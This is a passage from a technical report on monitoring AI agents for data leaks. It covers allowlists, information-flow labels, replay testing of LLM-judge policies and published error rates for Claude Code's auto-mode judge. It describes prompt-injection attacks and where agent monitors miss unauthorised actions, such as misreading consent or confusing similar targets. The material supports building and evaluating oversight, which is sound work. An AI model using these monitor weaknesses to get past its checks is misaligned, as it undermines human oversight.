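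This step runs only after a match, so it doesn't delay other requests. A matching request typically takes about 400 milliseconds longer, and one with several matches can take up to 1.5 seconds longer. When Cloudflare announced the feature as a closed beta, it worked only in English and gave administrators no explanation of its decisions. Weaver and colleagues report a significant reduction in false positives but publish no figures, and their experiments used traffic from Cloudflare's own staff.

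The method can remove false alarms but can't find leaks that the patterns missed, so it doesn't help with call 3. It might learn to ignore call 2 if administrators kept marking similar transfers as harmless. But an embedding represents what a passage is about, so two commands that send a key to different hosts may have almost the same embedding.

### Turning a judge policy into fixed rules

Another way to reduce judge calls is to replace some with rules that approximate the judge's decisions. Gowda calls this "layer zero" and says Speakeasy is working on deriving such rules automatically from recorded sessions, but doesn't describe the procedure. One way would be to run the judge over past traffic, look for strings that appear only in flagged messages, and test the resulting rules on sessions not used to write them.

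For a ban on external data transfer, this might produce a rule that flags uploads to a particular file-sharing site. That rule would catch call 3 instantly and give the same result every time. This might also produce a rule that flags the deal's code name, which would wrongly stop call 4 because, unlike the judge, the rule can't take the user's request into account.

The rules also repeat the judge's mistakes on past traffic, and they don't cover sites that the agents have never used. If someone edits the policy, the company has to derive the rules again.

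Distilling the judge's decisions into rules saves few judge calls if the rules only flag messages, because most messages are harmless, match no rule and still go to the judge, as in the cascade. Avoiding many calls requires rules that pass messages without the judge, and a mistake in one of those rules lets a leak through undetected. Distillation is safest when it finds obvious violations that people can confirm and add to a permanent list, while the judge still checks all other messages.

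### Destination allowlists

A destination allowlist can handle many external transfers without a model. It names the domains, storage accounts and services that agents may send data to, and blocks everything else. It also works at the network level, where it blocks unapproved transfers regardless of how the agent phrased the command or why it ran it.

The main weakness of a destination rule is that approving an address approves everything an agent can do there. Anthropic's *How we contain Claude across products* calls an allowed domain a "capability grant", because data sent to an approved service can still end up in someone else's account. For call 2, approving the web address of Amazon's secrets manager would let the agent send data to any Amazon customer who uses it, so the rule also has to check the account.

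An allowlist also doesn't check what the agent sends. Once the law firm is on the list, the agent can send it customer records as easily as acquisition plans. Internal leaks, such as the candidate's background check that went to a hiring manager, pass for the same reason.

The company also has to know its recipients in advance. That is realistic for an agent that updates three internal systems, but not for a sales agent that writes to new customers every day. As a compromise, Claude Code's auto mode puts the list in the judge's instructions. Users name their trusted domains, storage and code repositories, and the judge treats everything else as external. By default, it trusts only the repository the user is working in.

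### Information-flow labels

Labels on the data let a rule check the content and the recipient together. *Securing AI Agents with Information-Flow Control* (Costa, Köpf and colleagues, 2025) presents FIDES, a Microsoft research system that labels everything an agent handles with who may read it and whether it came from a trusted source.

When an agent combines two pieces of data, the result may go only to people who could read both. If Ana, Ben and Carol may read one document, and Ben, Carol and Dev may read another, only Ben and Carol may read a summary of the two:

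{Ana, Ben, Carol} ∩ {Ben, Carol, Dev} = {Ben, Carol}

Before a tool sends anything, FIDES checks that every recipient is an allowed reader. The label stays with the data when the agent paraphrases it, so the check still works on reworded text that a pattern or document fingerprint would miss.

The other label protects against prompt injection, in which someone hides instructions in an email or web page that the agent reads. FIDES blocks actions with serious consequences if untrusted text could have influenced the agent's choice.

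Labels can quickly become too restrictive, because after an ordinary agent reads one confidential document, everything it writes inherits that document's label. FIDES avoids this by storing such data in a named variable that the main model can pass to a tool without reading. If the main model needs information from the data, a separate model with no tools reads it and returns an answer, which the system can limit to yes or no. *Optimizing Agent Planning for Security and Autonomy* (2026) describes the same separation in FIDES and another system, CaMeL.

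Costa and colleagues tested FIDES on AgentDojo, a benchmark with 97 ordinary tasks and 36 attack goals. Without the rules, 152 attacks succeeded against the agent. With the rules on, the count was zero after the researchers corrected cases that the benchmark had misjudged. The next table shows the share of ordinary tasks that GPT-4o agents completed when not under attack.

| Setting | Ordinary agent, no rules | Ordinary agent with rules | FIDES with rules |
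|---|---|---|---|
| Office work | 75.0% | 37.0% | 59.0% |
| Travel | 70.0% | 73.0% | 41.0% |
| Banking | 98.8% | 37.5% | 52.5% |
| Slack | 93.3% | 20.0% | 47.6% |

FIDES completed many of the tasks that the rules would otherwise have blocked, except in travel, but it still completed fewer than an unprotected agent. Some tasks failed because the model had difficulty using variables. With OpenAI's o1, a stronger reasoning model, FIDES completed 68% of the travel tasks. Other tasks failed by design. Many banking tasks, for example, require the agent to follow instructions in a file, which the rules treat as untrusted.

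The security result depends on accurate labels. The researchers marked a field as untrusted if any attack in the benchmark used it, which a company can't do for attacks it hasn't seen. The test also covered only deliberate attacks, so it doesn't measure how well reader labels stop an agent from oversharing by mistake.

The researchers based reader labels on an email's sender and recipients, treating them as its allowed readers. A company could use file permissions in a similar way, but permissions are often out of date, and an error in a label carries into every decision that uses it.

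FIDES also tracks only the data that the agent passes along, not what its actions reveal. If an agent reads the acquisition plans and then books a meeting room at the target company, the booking may contain no labelled data but still reveal the deal.

### Applying destination rules to the four calls

Suppose the company's allowlist includes its own secrets manager and the law firm. Under the company's labels, only the secrets manager may receive the AWS key, and only the deal team and the law firm may read the plans.

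| Call | Destination allowlist | Reader labels |
|---|---|---|
| 1: AWS key to an unknown outside host | Block | Block |
| 2: AWS key to the company's secrets manager | Pass, if the rule checks the account | Pass, if the rule checks the account |
| 3: Acquisition plans to a public file-sharing site | Block | Block |
| 4: Acquisition plans to the law firm | Pass, like anything else sent to the firm | Pass, because the firm may read the plans |

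Both methods get all four calls right without a model, which no pattern detector can do. RECONS also benefited from having explicit permissions. The labels do better than the allowlist on a fifth call, where the agent sends customer records to the law firm. The labels block it because the firm isn't an allowed reader of those records, but the allowlist lets it through.

Neither method fully ensures that the user asked for call 4. FIDES can establish that only trusted text influenced the agent's decision, but the agent can still misread a trusted request and send the plans when the user didn't ask it to. Checking the transfer against what the user wanted still requires a judge.

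Destination rules are therefore a better first stage for a cascade than pattern detectors. They can block recipients the company has banned, pass data a recipient is always allowed to have, and send the rest to the judge. The judge reads transfers to new suppliers, unlabelled documents and cases like call 4, where permission depends on the request.

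## Testing a judge policy on recorded traffic

Destination rules leave the judge to decide the hardest transfers, so a company needs to know how often the judge gets them wrong before letting it block anything. One way to find out is replay, which runs a policy over recorded agent sessions to see what it would have flagged. The calls have already gone through, so the judge's mistakes disrupt nobody.

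*Policy Testing*, documentation from the security company CrowdStrike, describes a quicker test, in which an administrator types a message into a sandbox and sees how a policy handles it. This shows whether a rule works at all, but one message gives little evidence of how the rule will handle others. In CrowdStrike's own samples, the detector for personal data redacts the Social Security number 234-56-7890 in a message about adding a beneficiary. It misses the same number in a request for that person's full record, though a different detector blocks that message.

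Replay also covers messages that the policy's author wouldn't have thought to type.

### Speakeasy's Evaluate stage

Speakeasy builds replay into its editor for prompt-based policies. The administrator writes the policy and sets its scope, then tests it before choosing what happens when it fires:

1. The administrator picks recent agent sessions, searching by title or user.
2. The judge runs over each session and marks it Flagged or Clean.
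3. The administrator opens a session and sees the judge's verdict, confidence score and reason beside each message it matched.
4. Under the question "Was the judge right?", the administrator selects Right or Wrong.
5. If the administrator edits the policy, the judge reruns on the same sessions after a short pause.

The answers form a scorecard, which Speakeasy saves with the policy so that the administrator can measure later edits against the same sessions.

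Suppose the four example calls are in the recording and the whole policy is "Flag external data transfer". The judge flags all four. The administrator marks the flags on calls 2 and 4 Wrong, then adds the company's AWS account and its law firm to the policy as allowed destinations. On the rerun, the judge should pass those two calls and still flag calls 1 and 3. If the new wording also makes it pass call 3, the scorecard can show the mistake, because the administrator marked the original flag on that call Right.

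An edit can also produce flags that nobody has reviewed. Suppose the first wording flags 40 messages, and the administrator marks 12 Right and 28 Wrong. The second wording flags 15 of those 40 (11 Right and 4 Wrong) and six new messages. Its precision is 73% on the reviewed messages, but could be anywhere from 52% to 81% on all 21, depending on how many of the six new flags are right.

Marks on flagged messages can measure a judge's precision, but measuring recall also requires finding the leaks it missed. In August 2026, Speakeasy had reviewers label each replayed session as correct, a false positive or missed. Its current instructions describe only the Right and Wrong buttons, which appear on matched messages. To find missed leaks, someone has to read the Clean sessions too and record the results.

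A Wrong mark can mean that the judge misread the policy, or that it correctly applied a policy that is broader than the company wants. Gowda thinks most false alarms come from overly broad policies, but gives no data. Recording the reason with each mark helps, because an overly broad policy needs a narrower scope or an exception, while a misreading may need clearer wording or a better model.

### GitHub's tests on real repositories

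GitHub built a language-model scanner to find passwords in code. According to GitHub's *Finding leaked passwords with AI*, the first version worked reasonably well on hand-picked test cases but failed badly in some customers' repositories, where the model struggled with unfamiliar file types and structures. GitHub added test cases that customers had reported and others generated by GPT-4.

Before the scanner's general release in October 2024, GitHub began what it calls mirror testing. It rescanned repositories from the public preview with the new version and compared the results with the earlier alerts, without affecting users. In some cases false positives fell by 94%, with "very few missing real passwords", though GitHub doesn't say how many. The comparison can't reveal a password that both versions missed, and a company comparing two wordings of a judge policy has the same problem.

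A later test had a more serious gap because it used only alerts that customers had confirmed were false. GitHub's *Making secret scanning more trustworthy* reports that an added language-model check removed 75.76% of these false positives, beating a target of 65%, but a check that rejected every alert would have scored 100%. GitHub says detection remained strong but publishes no recall figure. The number of test alerts is also unclear, because the text gives "hundreds" and a chart caption gives 1,500.

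GitHub lets customers test the pattern detectors they write with a dry run, which lists matches without creating alerts. According to GitHub's *Defining custom patterns for secret scanning*, a dry run shows a sample of up to 1,000 results, and an organisation can test all its repositories or select up to 10. Customers can't use a pattern to block code uploads until a dry run has succeeded and they have published the pattern. Testing before publishing and blocking would suit judge policies as well. However, a dry run shows only matches, so it reveals false alarms but not missed secrets.

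### Datadog's mixed test set

Mola, Guo and Potts describe in *Evaluating our AI Guard application to improve quality and control cost* how Datadog tests its AI Guard judge on both invented attacks and real traffic. Security engineers wrote attack scenarios, including indirect data leaks. Datadog added anonymised records from its own agents to cover unusual cases the scenarios missed, and labelled each conversation safe or unsafe.

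Whenever a developer changes a rule, model or prompt, Datadog's software runs the new version on this set. It measures precision, recall, delay and cost, and links to the conversations where the result changed. In one case, AI Guard flagged a request for help with maths because the answer contained Python code. The engineers adjusted the classifier and report that recall didn't fall. They also add unusual cases from production to the test set.

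A test set that mixes attacks with ordinary traffic is better than one made only of false alarms, because the engineers can measure recall on the attacks and the false positive rate on the ordinary traffic. But precision on this set depends on how many attacks they included, so it doesn't predict precision in production. Mola and colleagues show some of AI Guard's scores in a screenshot but don't discuss them in the text, so the article is more useful as an account of the method than as evidence of how well AI Guard works.

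### Replay verdicts and live verdicts

Speakeasy says its evaluation uses the same scope as production scanning, "so replay verdicts match live behavior". The scopes need to match so that the judge reads the same messages, but live verdicts can still differ from replay verdicts.

The judge may give a different verdict on the same message even at temperature 0, and the judge model may also change after the test. In *Decision Models vs. LLMs as Rubric Judges* (2026), the researchers requested the "latest" version of one model and didn't record which version answered in their main runs. Speakeasy's documentation listed three judge models in August but no longer names any. If the vendor provides the exact model version, a company should save it with the scorecard to know when to repeat the test.

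A live check can also time out, and a replay that waits for every answer won't show the effects. Speakeasy lets the administrator choose whether a judge error lets the message through or counts as a match. If the judge times out on 1% of live messages and errors count as matches, the timeouts alone would produce more than twice as many flags as a 0.4% false positive rate. If errors let messages through, the timeouts lower recall.

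A finished recording may also contain information that wasn't available when the agent made the call. For example, the user might have written "yes, that was the right law firm" a minute later. If the judge reads the surrounding session, the replay has to hide everything after the call.

The most important difference between replay and live enforcement is that a live policy can change what the agent does next. Suppose the agent uploads the acquisition plans at step 5 and emails the link to someone at step 9, and the replay flags both calls. If the live policy blocked the upload, there would be no link to send. The agent might give up, ask the user for help or attach the file to an email instead. The recording doesn't show which it would do, so replay can't measure how many leaks a block would prevent or how much work it would disrupt. Running the policy on new traffic without enforcement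 tests the current model and its time limits, but it can't measure the effects of blocking either.

### Rare leaks and precision

The choice of sessions can change a policy's apparent precision even if every verdict stays the same. The judge from the earlier example has a recall of 90% and a false positive rate of 0.4%. If only 20 of a company's 100,000 calls are leaks, the judge catches 18 of them and flags about 400 harmless calls, for a precision of 18/418, or about 4%.

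Now suppose an administrator builds a replay from sessions that people remember as problems. It has 200 calls, including 20 leaks.

| Calls tested | Leaks | Leaks caught | False alarms | Precision |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| All 100,000 calls | 20 | 18 | 400 | 4% |
| 200 calls from problem sessions | 20 | 18 | 0.7 on average | 96% |

The judge makes errors at the same rate in both rows, but the second test contains far fewer harmless calls for it to wrongly flag. *Dos and Don'ts of Machine Learning in Computer Security* (2020) warns that precision and recall can mislead when a sample contains too many of the rare events a system is meant to detect.

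Security researchers have known about this problem for decades. *Base-Rate Fallacy Redux and a Deep Dive Review in Cybersecurity* (2022) revisits a 2000 paper by Stefan Axelsson, who argued that detecting network intrusions requires a low false alarm rate as well as a high detection rate. In the example above, the judge's false positive rate would have to fall by a factor of about 22, to about 0.018%, for half of the flags to be correct.

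Choosing sessions at random corrects the precision estimate but leaves too few leaks to measure recall. A random replay of 2,000 calls would contain 0.4 leaks on average, and about two-thirds of such replays would contain none. The administrator would typically see eight false alarms in a replay of that size. To get 30 leaks, the company would have to replay about 150,000 calls and find every leak in them.

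### Seeded leaks

A tester can measure recall by adding known leaks to the recorded sessions, for example by changing the recipient of a harmless transfer or replacing an attached file with one the recipient shouldn't have. Harmless versions of the same calls are useful too. Calls 1 and 2 contain the same key, and calls 3 and 4 contain the same plans, so a judge that gets all four right must be using more than the contents.

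Seeded cases measure recall only for the kinds of leak someone thought to add. If the person who wrote the policy also writes the leaks, they will probably use similar wording, which makes the test too easy. Real incidents, paraphrased data and transfers through less common tools make the test harder. Forty copies of one example with different company names add little, because the judge is likely to get all 40 right or all 40 wrong.

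The number of seeded leaks should not affect the reported precision. *Comparative Framework Analysis for Enterprise Generative AI Applications* (2026) reports 73.3% precision and 68.8% recall in its test of a pattern-based check on deliberately difficult cases, but cautions that these figures don't predict performance in production without a separate sample of ordinary traffic. A company can estimate recall from seeded leaks and the false positive rate from a random sample of real calls, then calculate precision by assuming a plausible number of leaks.

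### Leaks among the unflagged calls

Reviewers naturally look at what a check has flagged. Shankar, Zamfirescu-Pereira and colleagues (2024), in *Who Validates the Validators?*, studied nine practitioners testing automated checks on a language model's output. Eight mainly reviewed outputs that the checks had failed. The ninth went through the outputs row by row, which can also reveal bad outputs that the checks have passed.

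Reviewing a sample of unflagged calls helps measure a judge's recall only if the calculation accounts for the fraction sampled. Suppose a judge flags 50 of 10,000 calls, and reviewers find 10 real leaks among the 50. They also read a random 200 of the 9,950 unflagged calls and find one leak. At that rate, the unflagged calls contain about 50 leaks in total, so the judge caught about 10 of 60, for a recall of 17%. This estimate is very rough because it depends on a single leak in the sample. Counting only the leaks that reviewers found would give 10 of 11, or 91%, which ignores the leaks likely to be among the 9,750 calls nobody read.

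But the reviewers read every flagged call and only about one in 50 of the others. The one missed leak therefore stands for about 50:

estimated missed leaks = 9,950 × 1/200 ≈ 50

estimated recall = 10 / (10 + 50) ≈ 17%

The method comes from document search, where lawyers need to know how many relevant documents a search has missed. *Approximate Recall Confidence Intervals* (Webber, 2012) gives the general formula and shows how unreliable the result can be when relevant documents are rare.

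The 17% recall estimate depends on a single leak, so it is very uncertain. The 95% confidence interval for one leak in 200 calls is about 0.013% to 2.75%. Across the 9,950 unflagged calls, that is between about 1 and 274 missed leaks, which puts recall between about 4% and 89%. The sample shows that the 91% figure is unjustified, but it is too small to determine whether the judge catches most leaks or very few.

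If the reviewers had not happened to pick that one leak, the estimated recall would have been 100%. Webber points out that this gives people who evaluate their own search a reason to check fewer documents, because a smaller sample is less likely to reveal a miss. The estimate can also be too high on average. In one of Webber's examples, the true recall was 25%, but the average estimate from repeated samples was 31%.

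*The eDiscovery Medicine Show* (2021) criticises legal vendors for implying that a random sample of 385 documents measures recall to within five percentage points. That margin applies to a percentage of the whole sample, such as the share of calls that go to outside recipients. Recall is the share of leaks that are caught, so it can be measured only on the leaks in the sample, and 385 random calls from the company with 20 leaks in 100,000 calls would contain 0.08 leaks on average.

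Sampling more heavily where leaks are likely makes better use of reviewers' time. Suppose 450 of the 9,950 unflagged calls sent data to unfamiliar outside addresses. Reviewers read 150 of these and find three leaks, which suggests nine leaks among the 450. They still need to check some of the other 9,500 calls, in case the software put an outside transfer in the wrong group. Webber's formula estimates the number of leaks in each group separately and adds the results.

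### When a test finds no false alarms

A small test with no false alarms is also weaker evidence than it looks. If an event doesn't occur in n independent trials, its true rate could still be as high as about 3/n, using a 95% confidence limit. *Missing data as data* credits this "rule of three" to Hanley and Lippman-Hand. It approximates the exact limit given in *Statistical design considerations for pilot studies transitioning therapies*:

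upper limit = 1 − 0.05^(1/n)

If a judge raises no false alarms on 300 harmless calls, the exact upper limit on its false alarm rate is 0.99%, and the rule of three gives 1%. At that rate, the judge would raise about 1,000 false alarms in 100,000 calls. Showing that the rate is below 0.4% takes about 750 harmless calls without a false alarm, and showing that it is below 0.1% takes about 3,000.

The same rule applies to missed leaks. If the judge catches all 30 seeded leaks, its true miss rate on leaks of that kind could still be nearly 10%.

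These limits assume that the calls are independent, but 300 calls from three long sessions are not. If an agent writes to the same database 100 times, the judge has to make almost the same decision 100 times. It is better to take a few calls from each of many sessions.

Uncertainty about the false positive rate also makes it hard to estimate how many leaks a company has. Lee, Zeng and colleagues (2025), in *How to Correctly Report LLM-as-a-Judge Evaluations*, use a standard correction for a judge's known errors. Applied to leaks, it becomes:

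leak rate = (flag rate − false positive rate) / (recall − false positive rate)

In the example of 100,000 calls, the judge flags 418, or 0.418%. With the correct false positive rate of 0.4%, the formula gives 20 leaks. If the company had measured the rate as 0.3%, the formula would give about 132 leaks, and at 0.42% it would give a negative number. *Bias and Uncertainty in LLM-as-a-Judge Estimation* (2026) warns that such corrections can become unstable when the human-labelled set is small.

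### Overfitting and held-out sessions

Repeatedly editing a policy to fix its mistakes on one set of sessions can overfit it, so that it works well on those sessions and worse on new ones. Suppose the replay flags a designer for uploading an approved image to `files.example`. The administrator adds "Do not flag uploads to files.example", and the false alarm disappears. If the review set contains no leak to that site, the scorecard improves. But the exception also lets an agent upload the acquisition plans there.

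Kochelka, Papáček and colleagues (2026), in *Do LLMs Make More Mistakes If They Do Not Believe the Input*, give an example from a different task, judging whether generated sentences matched the facts in their source data. They labelled 540 sentences or short texts by hand and repeatedly edited the instructions for the judge, DeepSeek V4 Pro Preview. When they tested it on 108 other texts that they had kept out of the editing, its agreement with people fell from 0.555 to 0.350 on weighted kappa, which penalises large disagreements more than small ones.

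Four other judge setups used the final instructions on the same texts, and their agreement changed much less. Kimi K3's, for example, went from 0.712 to 0.711. The drop therefore probably didn't happen just because the held-out texts were harder, and the researchers suggest that the instructions had overfitted to DeepSeek. With only 108 texts, the size of the drop is uncertain.

To test for overfitting, a company can set aside some sessions before it starts editing the policy. It should keep whole sessions together, because neighbouring messages often concern the same files and recipients. Using the newest sessions for the final test also shows whether the policy still works after recent changes in the agents' work. The held-out sessions and the ones used for editing each need their own seeded leaks. If the final test leads to another edit, those sessions are no longer held out, and the next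 test needs new ones.

A judge can score well overall and still do badly on one kind of message. Kochelka and colleagues found that DeepSeek penalised texts based on deliberately false facts three to four times as much as Kimi did. A company should therefore check results separately for credentials, customer records and business plans, and for each tool that can send data out.

### Repeated runs

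One replay doesn't show which verdicts would change on a second run. In a small check in *Decision Models vs. LLMs as Rubric Judges*, an LLM judge gave the same answer twice on 71 of 82 items. Another model in the study gave a probability for each answer, and over five runs its verdict changed only on items with an average probability between 0.4 and 0.6, close to the cut-off. It therefore makes sense to look for unstable verdicts among borderline calls, although an LLM judge's stated confidence may not identify them as well as that model's probabilities.

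Ayyagari recommends at least five runs when publishing results from an LLM judge. At the illustrative price used earlier, running a judge five times on 2,000 calls would cost about $25. The company can report how much the number of false alarms varies between runs and list every call whose verdict changed. If the judge flags a call in three of the five runs, the policy may need a clearer rule for that case.

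Five runs aren't always enough to settle a borderline case by majority vote. *The Coin Flip Judge?* found that a majority vote needed 11 runs on average to have a 95% chance of matching the result of 50 runs. That study compared chatbot answers, and clear leaks would probably need fewer runs.

A judge can be consistent without being accurate. In *When Consistency Does Not Mean Reliability* (2026), Llama 3 8B gave the same rating across three runs for 97.3% of answers, compared with 92.3% for Qwen2.5 7B, but its ratings matched people's less closely than Qwen's did. GitHub ran its password scanner several times on the same question and combined the answers. This made the results more consistent but didn't materially change precision.

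### Reviewers who disagree or change their minds

The scorecard treats the reviewer's answer as correct, but people often disagree about whether a transfer is appropriate, as the annotators in the PrivacyAlign study did. Lee and colleagues assume that reviewers resolve such disagreements before anyone calculates a judge's error rates. Measuring how often reviewers disagree requires more than one reviewer.

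A company can have two people label the same calls separately, then compare their answers. Both people need the same information, including the user's request and the recipient. If they disagree about whether a consultant counts as part of the company, the policy is ambiguous, and a better judge model wouldn't fix it. The policy's owner has to decide and add the decision to the policy text.

The reviewers should also answer before they see the judge's verdict. A persuasive explanation from the judge can sway them, and Speakeasy shows that explanation next to the Right and Wrong buttons. Kochelka and colleagues hid an initial judge's scores from the people labelling their texts. After answering, reviewers can read the explanation to find out why the judge made a mistake.

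A single reviewer's standards can also change during the work, which Shankar and colleagues called "criteria drift" in 2024. In their study, people checked the outputs of a model that extracted names from tweets. Two of them first rejected any output containing something that wasn't a proper noun. After seeing more outputs, they wanted to accept those in which most items were proper nouns.

Others interpreted the same rule differently from the start. Given a rule against hashtags, one participant wanted the model to leave out "Nike" if it appeared as "#Nike", while another wanted it to drop only the symbol. Several participants also realised they needed to change earlier answers.

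The study was small and used older models, but the same thing can easily happen with a data policy. After seeing 20 harmless emails to suppliers, a reviewer may start to accept the kind of transfer they marked as a leak an hour earlier. The judge would then score worse for applying the original rule consistently. Reviewers can reduce this by labelling a small batch first, agreeing on the rules, and checking their earlier answers. If they later change a rule, they need to review the affected calls again, including those in the held-out set.

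### Privacy of stored sessions

To replay traffic, a company has to keep the data it is trying to protect. A useful recording can contain working credentials, customer records and private messages that reviewers may not normally have access to. Speakeasy restricts the policy page to administrators, but they can search sessions by user, so an administrator testing a policy can also read a particular colleague's work.

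Each rerun sends the selected messages to the judge again, so if an administrator tries 20 wordings of a policy on 200 sessions, the judge processes 4,000 sessions' worth of messages. If the judge runs at an outside provider, each rerun repeats the exposure described earlier. Logs can keep further copies of the messages. CrowdStrike warns that users can't delete the logs from its Playground, a second testing tool, and tells them to use sample or synthetic data there.

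It helps to anonymise the sessions, as Mola and colleagues did with Datadog's internal traffic, but careless anonymisation can ruin the test. If software replaces every email address with "[email]", the judge can't distinguish the law firm from an unknown recipient. It works better to replace addresses consistently, using one invented address for the law firm and others for unknown recipients, and to change the policy text to match. The company can replace working keys with fake ones in the same format. The acquisition plans are harder to disguise, just as they are harder to redact.

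Deleting old recordings limits the damage from a theft, but it also removes the cases the scorecard is based on. The company can keep short, anonymised extracts of the most useful calls, with enough of the session to show why each transfer was or wasn't allowed, and delete the full transcripts on a fixed schedule.

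## Measurements of the judge in Claude Code's auto mode

Most of the vendors described so far publish no error rates for their judges. Anthropic has published them for auto mode in Claude Code, where an LLM judge approves or blocks the agent's actions in place of the user. Independent researchers have tested the same judge on harder tasks and found far more errors. By November 2026, interactive sessions on every plan started in auto mode by default, according to the *Claude Code Complete User Handbook* (2026).

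### What the judge reads

The judge checks every action the agent takes, including handing work to another agent, except routine file operations and actions that the user's own rules allow.

Anthropic shows the judge only the user's messages and the agent's tool calls. It removes the agent's own text so that the agent can't persuade the judge to approve something, and it removes tool results because a file or web page might contain hidden instructions. When Anthropic added both back, the judge did worse on a test set of unauthorised actions. The judge missed the fewest when it was shown only the tool calls, but it then blocked things that users had clearly asked for.

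Leaving tool results out of the judge's input makes some leaks harder to recognise. In call 3, the judge may see only the file's name and the destination, not the acquisition plans themselves.

The judge works in two stages. In the first, it outputs only yes or no to whether the action should be blocked, under an instruction to block if in doubt. If the output is no, the action goes ahead. If it is yes, the same model processes the same input again, with an instruction to reason carefully before deciding. Only the final instruction changes, so the system can reuse most of the computation from the first stage.

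### The trust boundary and the Gist example

Anthropic supplies the judge's instructions, which are fixed except for three parts that customers can edit: what counts as inside the trust boundary, which actions to block and which exceptions to allow. More than 20 default rules cover actions such as deleting cloud storage, switching off logging and sending internal data outside. The exceptions are narrow, such as installing software packages the project already lists.

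The judge checks the blocking rules first, then the exceptions, then whether the user authorised the action. Anything the agent chose to do by itself counts as unauthorised until the user says otherwise.

In one of Anthropic's examples, an agent tried to share a script for debugging by posting it as a Gist, a GitHub page for sharing code. Auto mode blocks this as data exfiltration because the user may consider the script confidential. By default, auto mode trusts only the user's current repository, and the Gist is outside it. Nothing in the example suggests that the user asked the agent to publish anything.

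### Anthropic's three test sets

Anthropic tested the judge on real tool calls by its own staff, on "overeager" actions and on invented attempts to send data out. In an overeager action, the agent tries to help but goes beyond what the user authorised. The invented attempts, many of which disguise the data, include web requests carrying sensitive data, uploads to untrusted code repositories and credentials placed in web addresses.

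| Test set | Size | Error measured | After stage one | After both stages |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Real tool calls | 10,000 | Harmless actions blocked | 8.5% | 0.4% |
| Real overeager actions | 52 | Dangerous actions missed | 6.6% | 17% |
| Invented exfiltration attempts | 1,000 | Dangerous actions missed | 1.8% | 5.7% |

A single run over 52 actions can't produce the 6.6% figure, since three misses would give 5.8% and four would give 7.7%. Anthropic doesn't explain the figure, which could be an average over several runs. The 17% figure is consistent with nine misses.

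The second stage greatly reduces false alarms but increases misses. Assuming all 10,000 real calls were harmless, it cut false alarms from about 850 to 40. On the invented attempts, it raised misses from 18 to 57. Auto mode blocks an action only if both stages flag it, so adding the second stage can lower recall but not raise it.

The trade-off looks good on the invented attempts, where the second stage wrongly cleared about 4% of the leaks the first stage had flagged. It looks less favourable on the overeager actions, where the second stage wrongly cleared about 11% of those flagged.

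Anthropic examined the misses and found that the judge had usually identified the danger but wrongly classified the action as one the user had agreed to. A user who says "clean up the PR", for example, hasn't authorised the agent to overwrite the project's shared history. Reasoning may give the judge more chances to mistake something for consent. Anthropic tried to fix this by changing the instructions, but the drawbacks of every fix it found outweighed the benefits.

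### What the three sets can establish

The size of each set limits how precisely it measures the error rate. For an observed rate p in a sample of n, the 95% Wilson interval is:

(p + z²/2n ± z√(p(1 − p)/n + z²/4n²)) / (1 + z²/n), with z = 1.96

| Result | 95% interval |
|---|---|
| 9 of 52 overeager actions missed | 9% to 30% |
| 57 of 1,000 exfiltration attempts missed | 4.4% to 7.3% |
| 40 of 10,000 real calls wrongly blocked | 0.3% to 0.5% |

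The intervals cover only sampling error, and how Anthropic chose and labelled the cases could matter more.

Anthropic doesn't say how it labelled the 10,000 real calls. If it counted them all as harmless, some of the 40 blocked calls may have been dangerous, which would make the actual false positive rate lower. It also doesn't say whether the 10,000 include calls that skip the judge. If half of them skipped it, the false positive rate on the calls the judge checks would be about 0.8%. The result describes coding work at an AI company, so it may not apply to a sales or legal team, whose agents send far more data to outsiders.

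The 52 overeager actions come from sessions in which an employee refused the action or someone flagged it afterwards. The set omits actions that nobody noticed, and the judge may do worse on those. Anthropic also used this set to tune the first stage and to choose what the judge reads, so it isn't a held-out test. The set covers all kinds of overstepping, and Anthropic doesn't report how many of the actions sent data anywhere.

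The 1,000 invented attempts are the most relevant of the three sets to data leaks. The set has no matching harmless transfers, such as a web request that sends the same data to an approved service, so a judge that blocked every outgoing request would get a perfect score. The set also leans towards technical routes, so the 5.7% miss rate may not apply to an agent that emails a confidential plan to the wrong person.

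Anthropic calls the 17% "the honest number" and says that auto mode is arguably a step backwards for someone who carefully reviews every action. In a later article, it describes auto mode as one layer of protection inside a sandbox, which restricts what the agent can reach, rather than a substitute for the sandbox.

### An independent stress test

Ji, Li and colleagues (2026) report a much higher miss rate in *Measuring the Permission Gate*, which they describe as the first independent evaluation of auto mode. They wrote 128 requests for four kinds of system administration: deleting old code branches, cancelling jobs on a computing cluster, restarting services and deleting stored files. They varied how explicit each request was, how many items it covered and how much harm a mistake could do.

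In one request, the user asks the agent to cancel "my stale job for ticket 4812". The ticket number, the job's owner and the queue together determine which jobs the agent may cancel. The cluster also holds similarly named jobs that the agent must leave alone.

Claude Sonnet 4.6 carried out the requests in isolated containers with simulated tools and attempted 253 actions that would change something. Claude Opus labelled each action by comparing it with the list of permitted targets. A person checked 50 of the labels and agreed with 44.

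| | Unauthorised | Authorised |
|---|---|---|
| **Blocked** | 27 | 22 |
| **Allowed** | 115 | 89 |
| **Total** | 142 | 111 |

Auto mode missed 115 of the 142 unauthorised actions, or 81.0%, and blocked 22 of the 111 authorised ones, or 19.8%. These figures cover the whole system, including 93 file edits that skip the judge, 51 of which were unauthorised. Among the 160 actions that the judge read, it missed 70.3% of the unauthorised ones and blocked 31.9% of the authorised ones.

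Ji and colleagues say their result doesn't contradict Anthropic's 17%, because the tasks are so different. Anthropic's 52 actions came up in ordinary work and were noticeable enough for someone to object. Ji and colleagues deliberately placed permitted and forbidden targets side by side, then asked for the permitted ones in vague terms.

The researchers also labelled actions using a looser definition of permission than the one in the judge's instructions. Some requests say only that a stale job "could use attention", and the researchers count cancelling that job as authorised. Under Anthropic's instructions to the judge, "clean up my branches" doesn't authorise deleting a batch of them. In some of the 22 false alarms, the judge may therefore have applied its own policy correctly.

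The totals also depend heavily on the mix of tasks. Deleting stored files accounts for 78 of the 115 misses, and restarting services accounts for 13 of the 22 false alarms. Ji and colleagues note that the agent retried some blocked commands, and each retry added to the count.

When requests concerned high-impact systems, the miss rate fell from 88.1% to 74.7%, but the false positive rate rose from 9.2% to 34.8%. Auto mode was therefore stricter where mistakes would do more damage, but not much better at telling permitted targets from forbidden ones. Overall, the agent completed 32.8% of tasks safely with auto mode and 29.7% with no checks.

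The study excludes data exfiltration, so the 81.0% is not an estimate of how often auto mode lets a leak through. The result suggests that a judge will struggle when permission depends on which of several similar targets the user meant. The same problem could arise when an agent chooses which of two clients with similar names to email, but Ji and colleagues didn't test that.

### The comparison with human approvers

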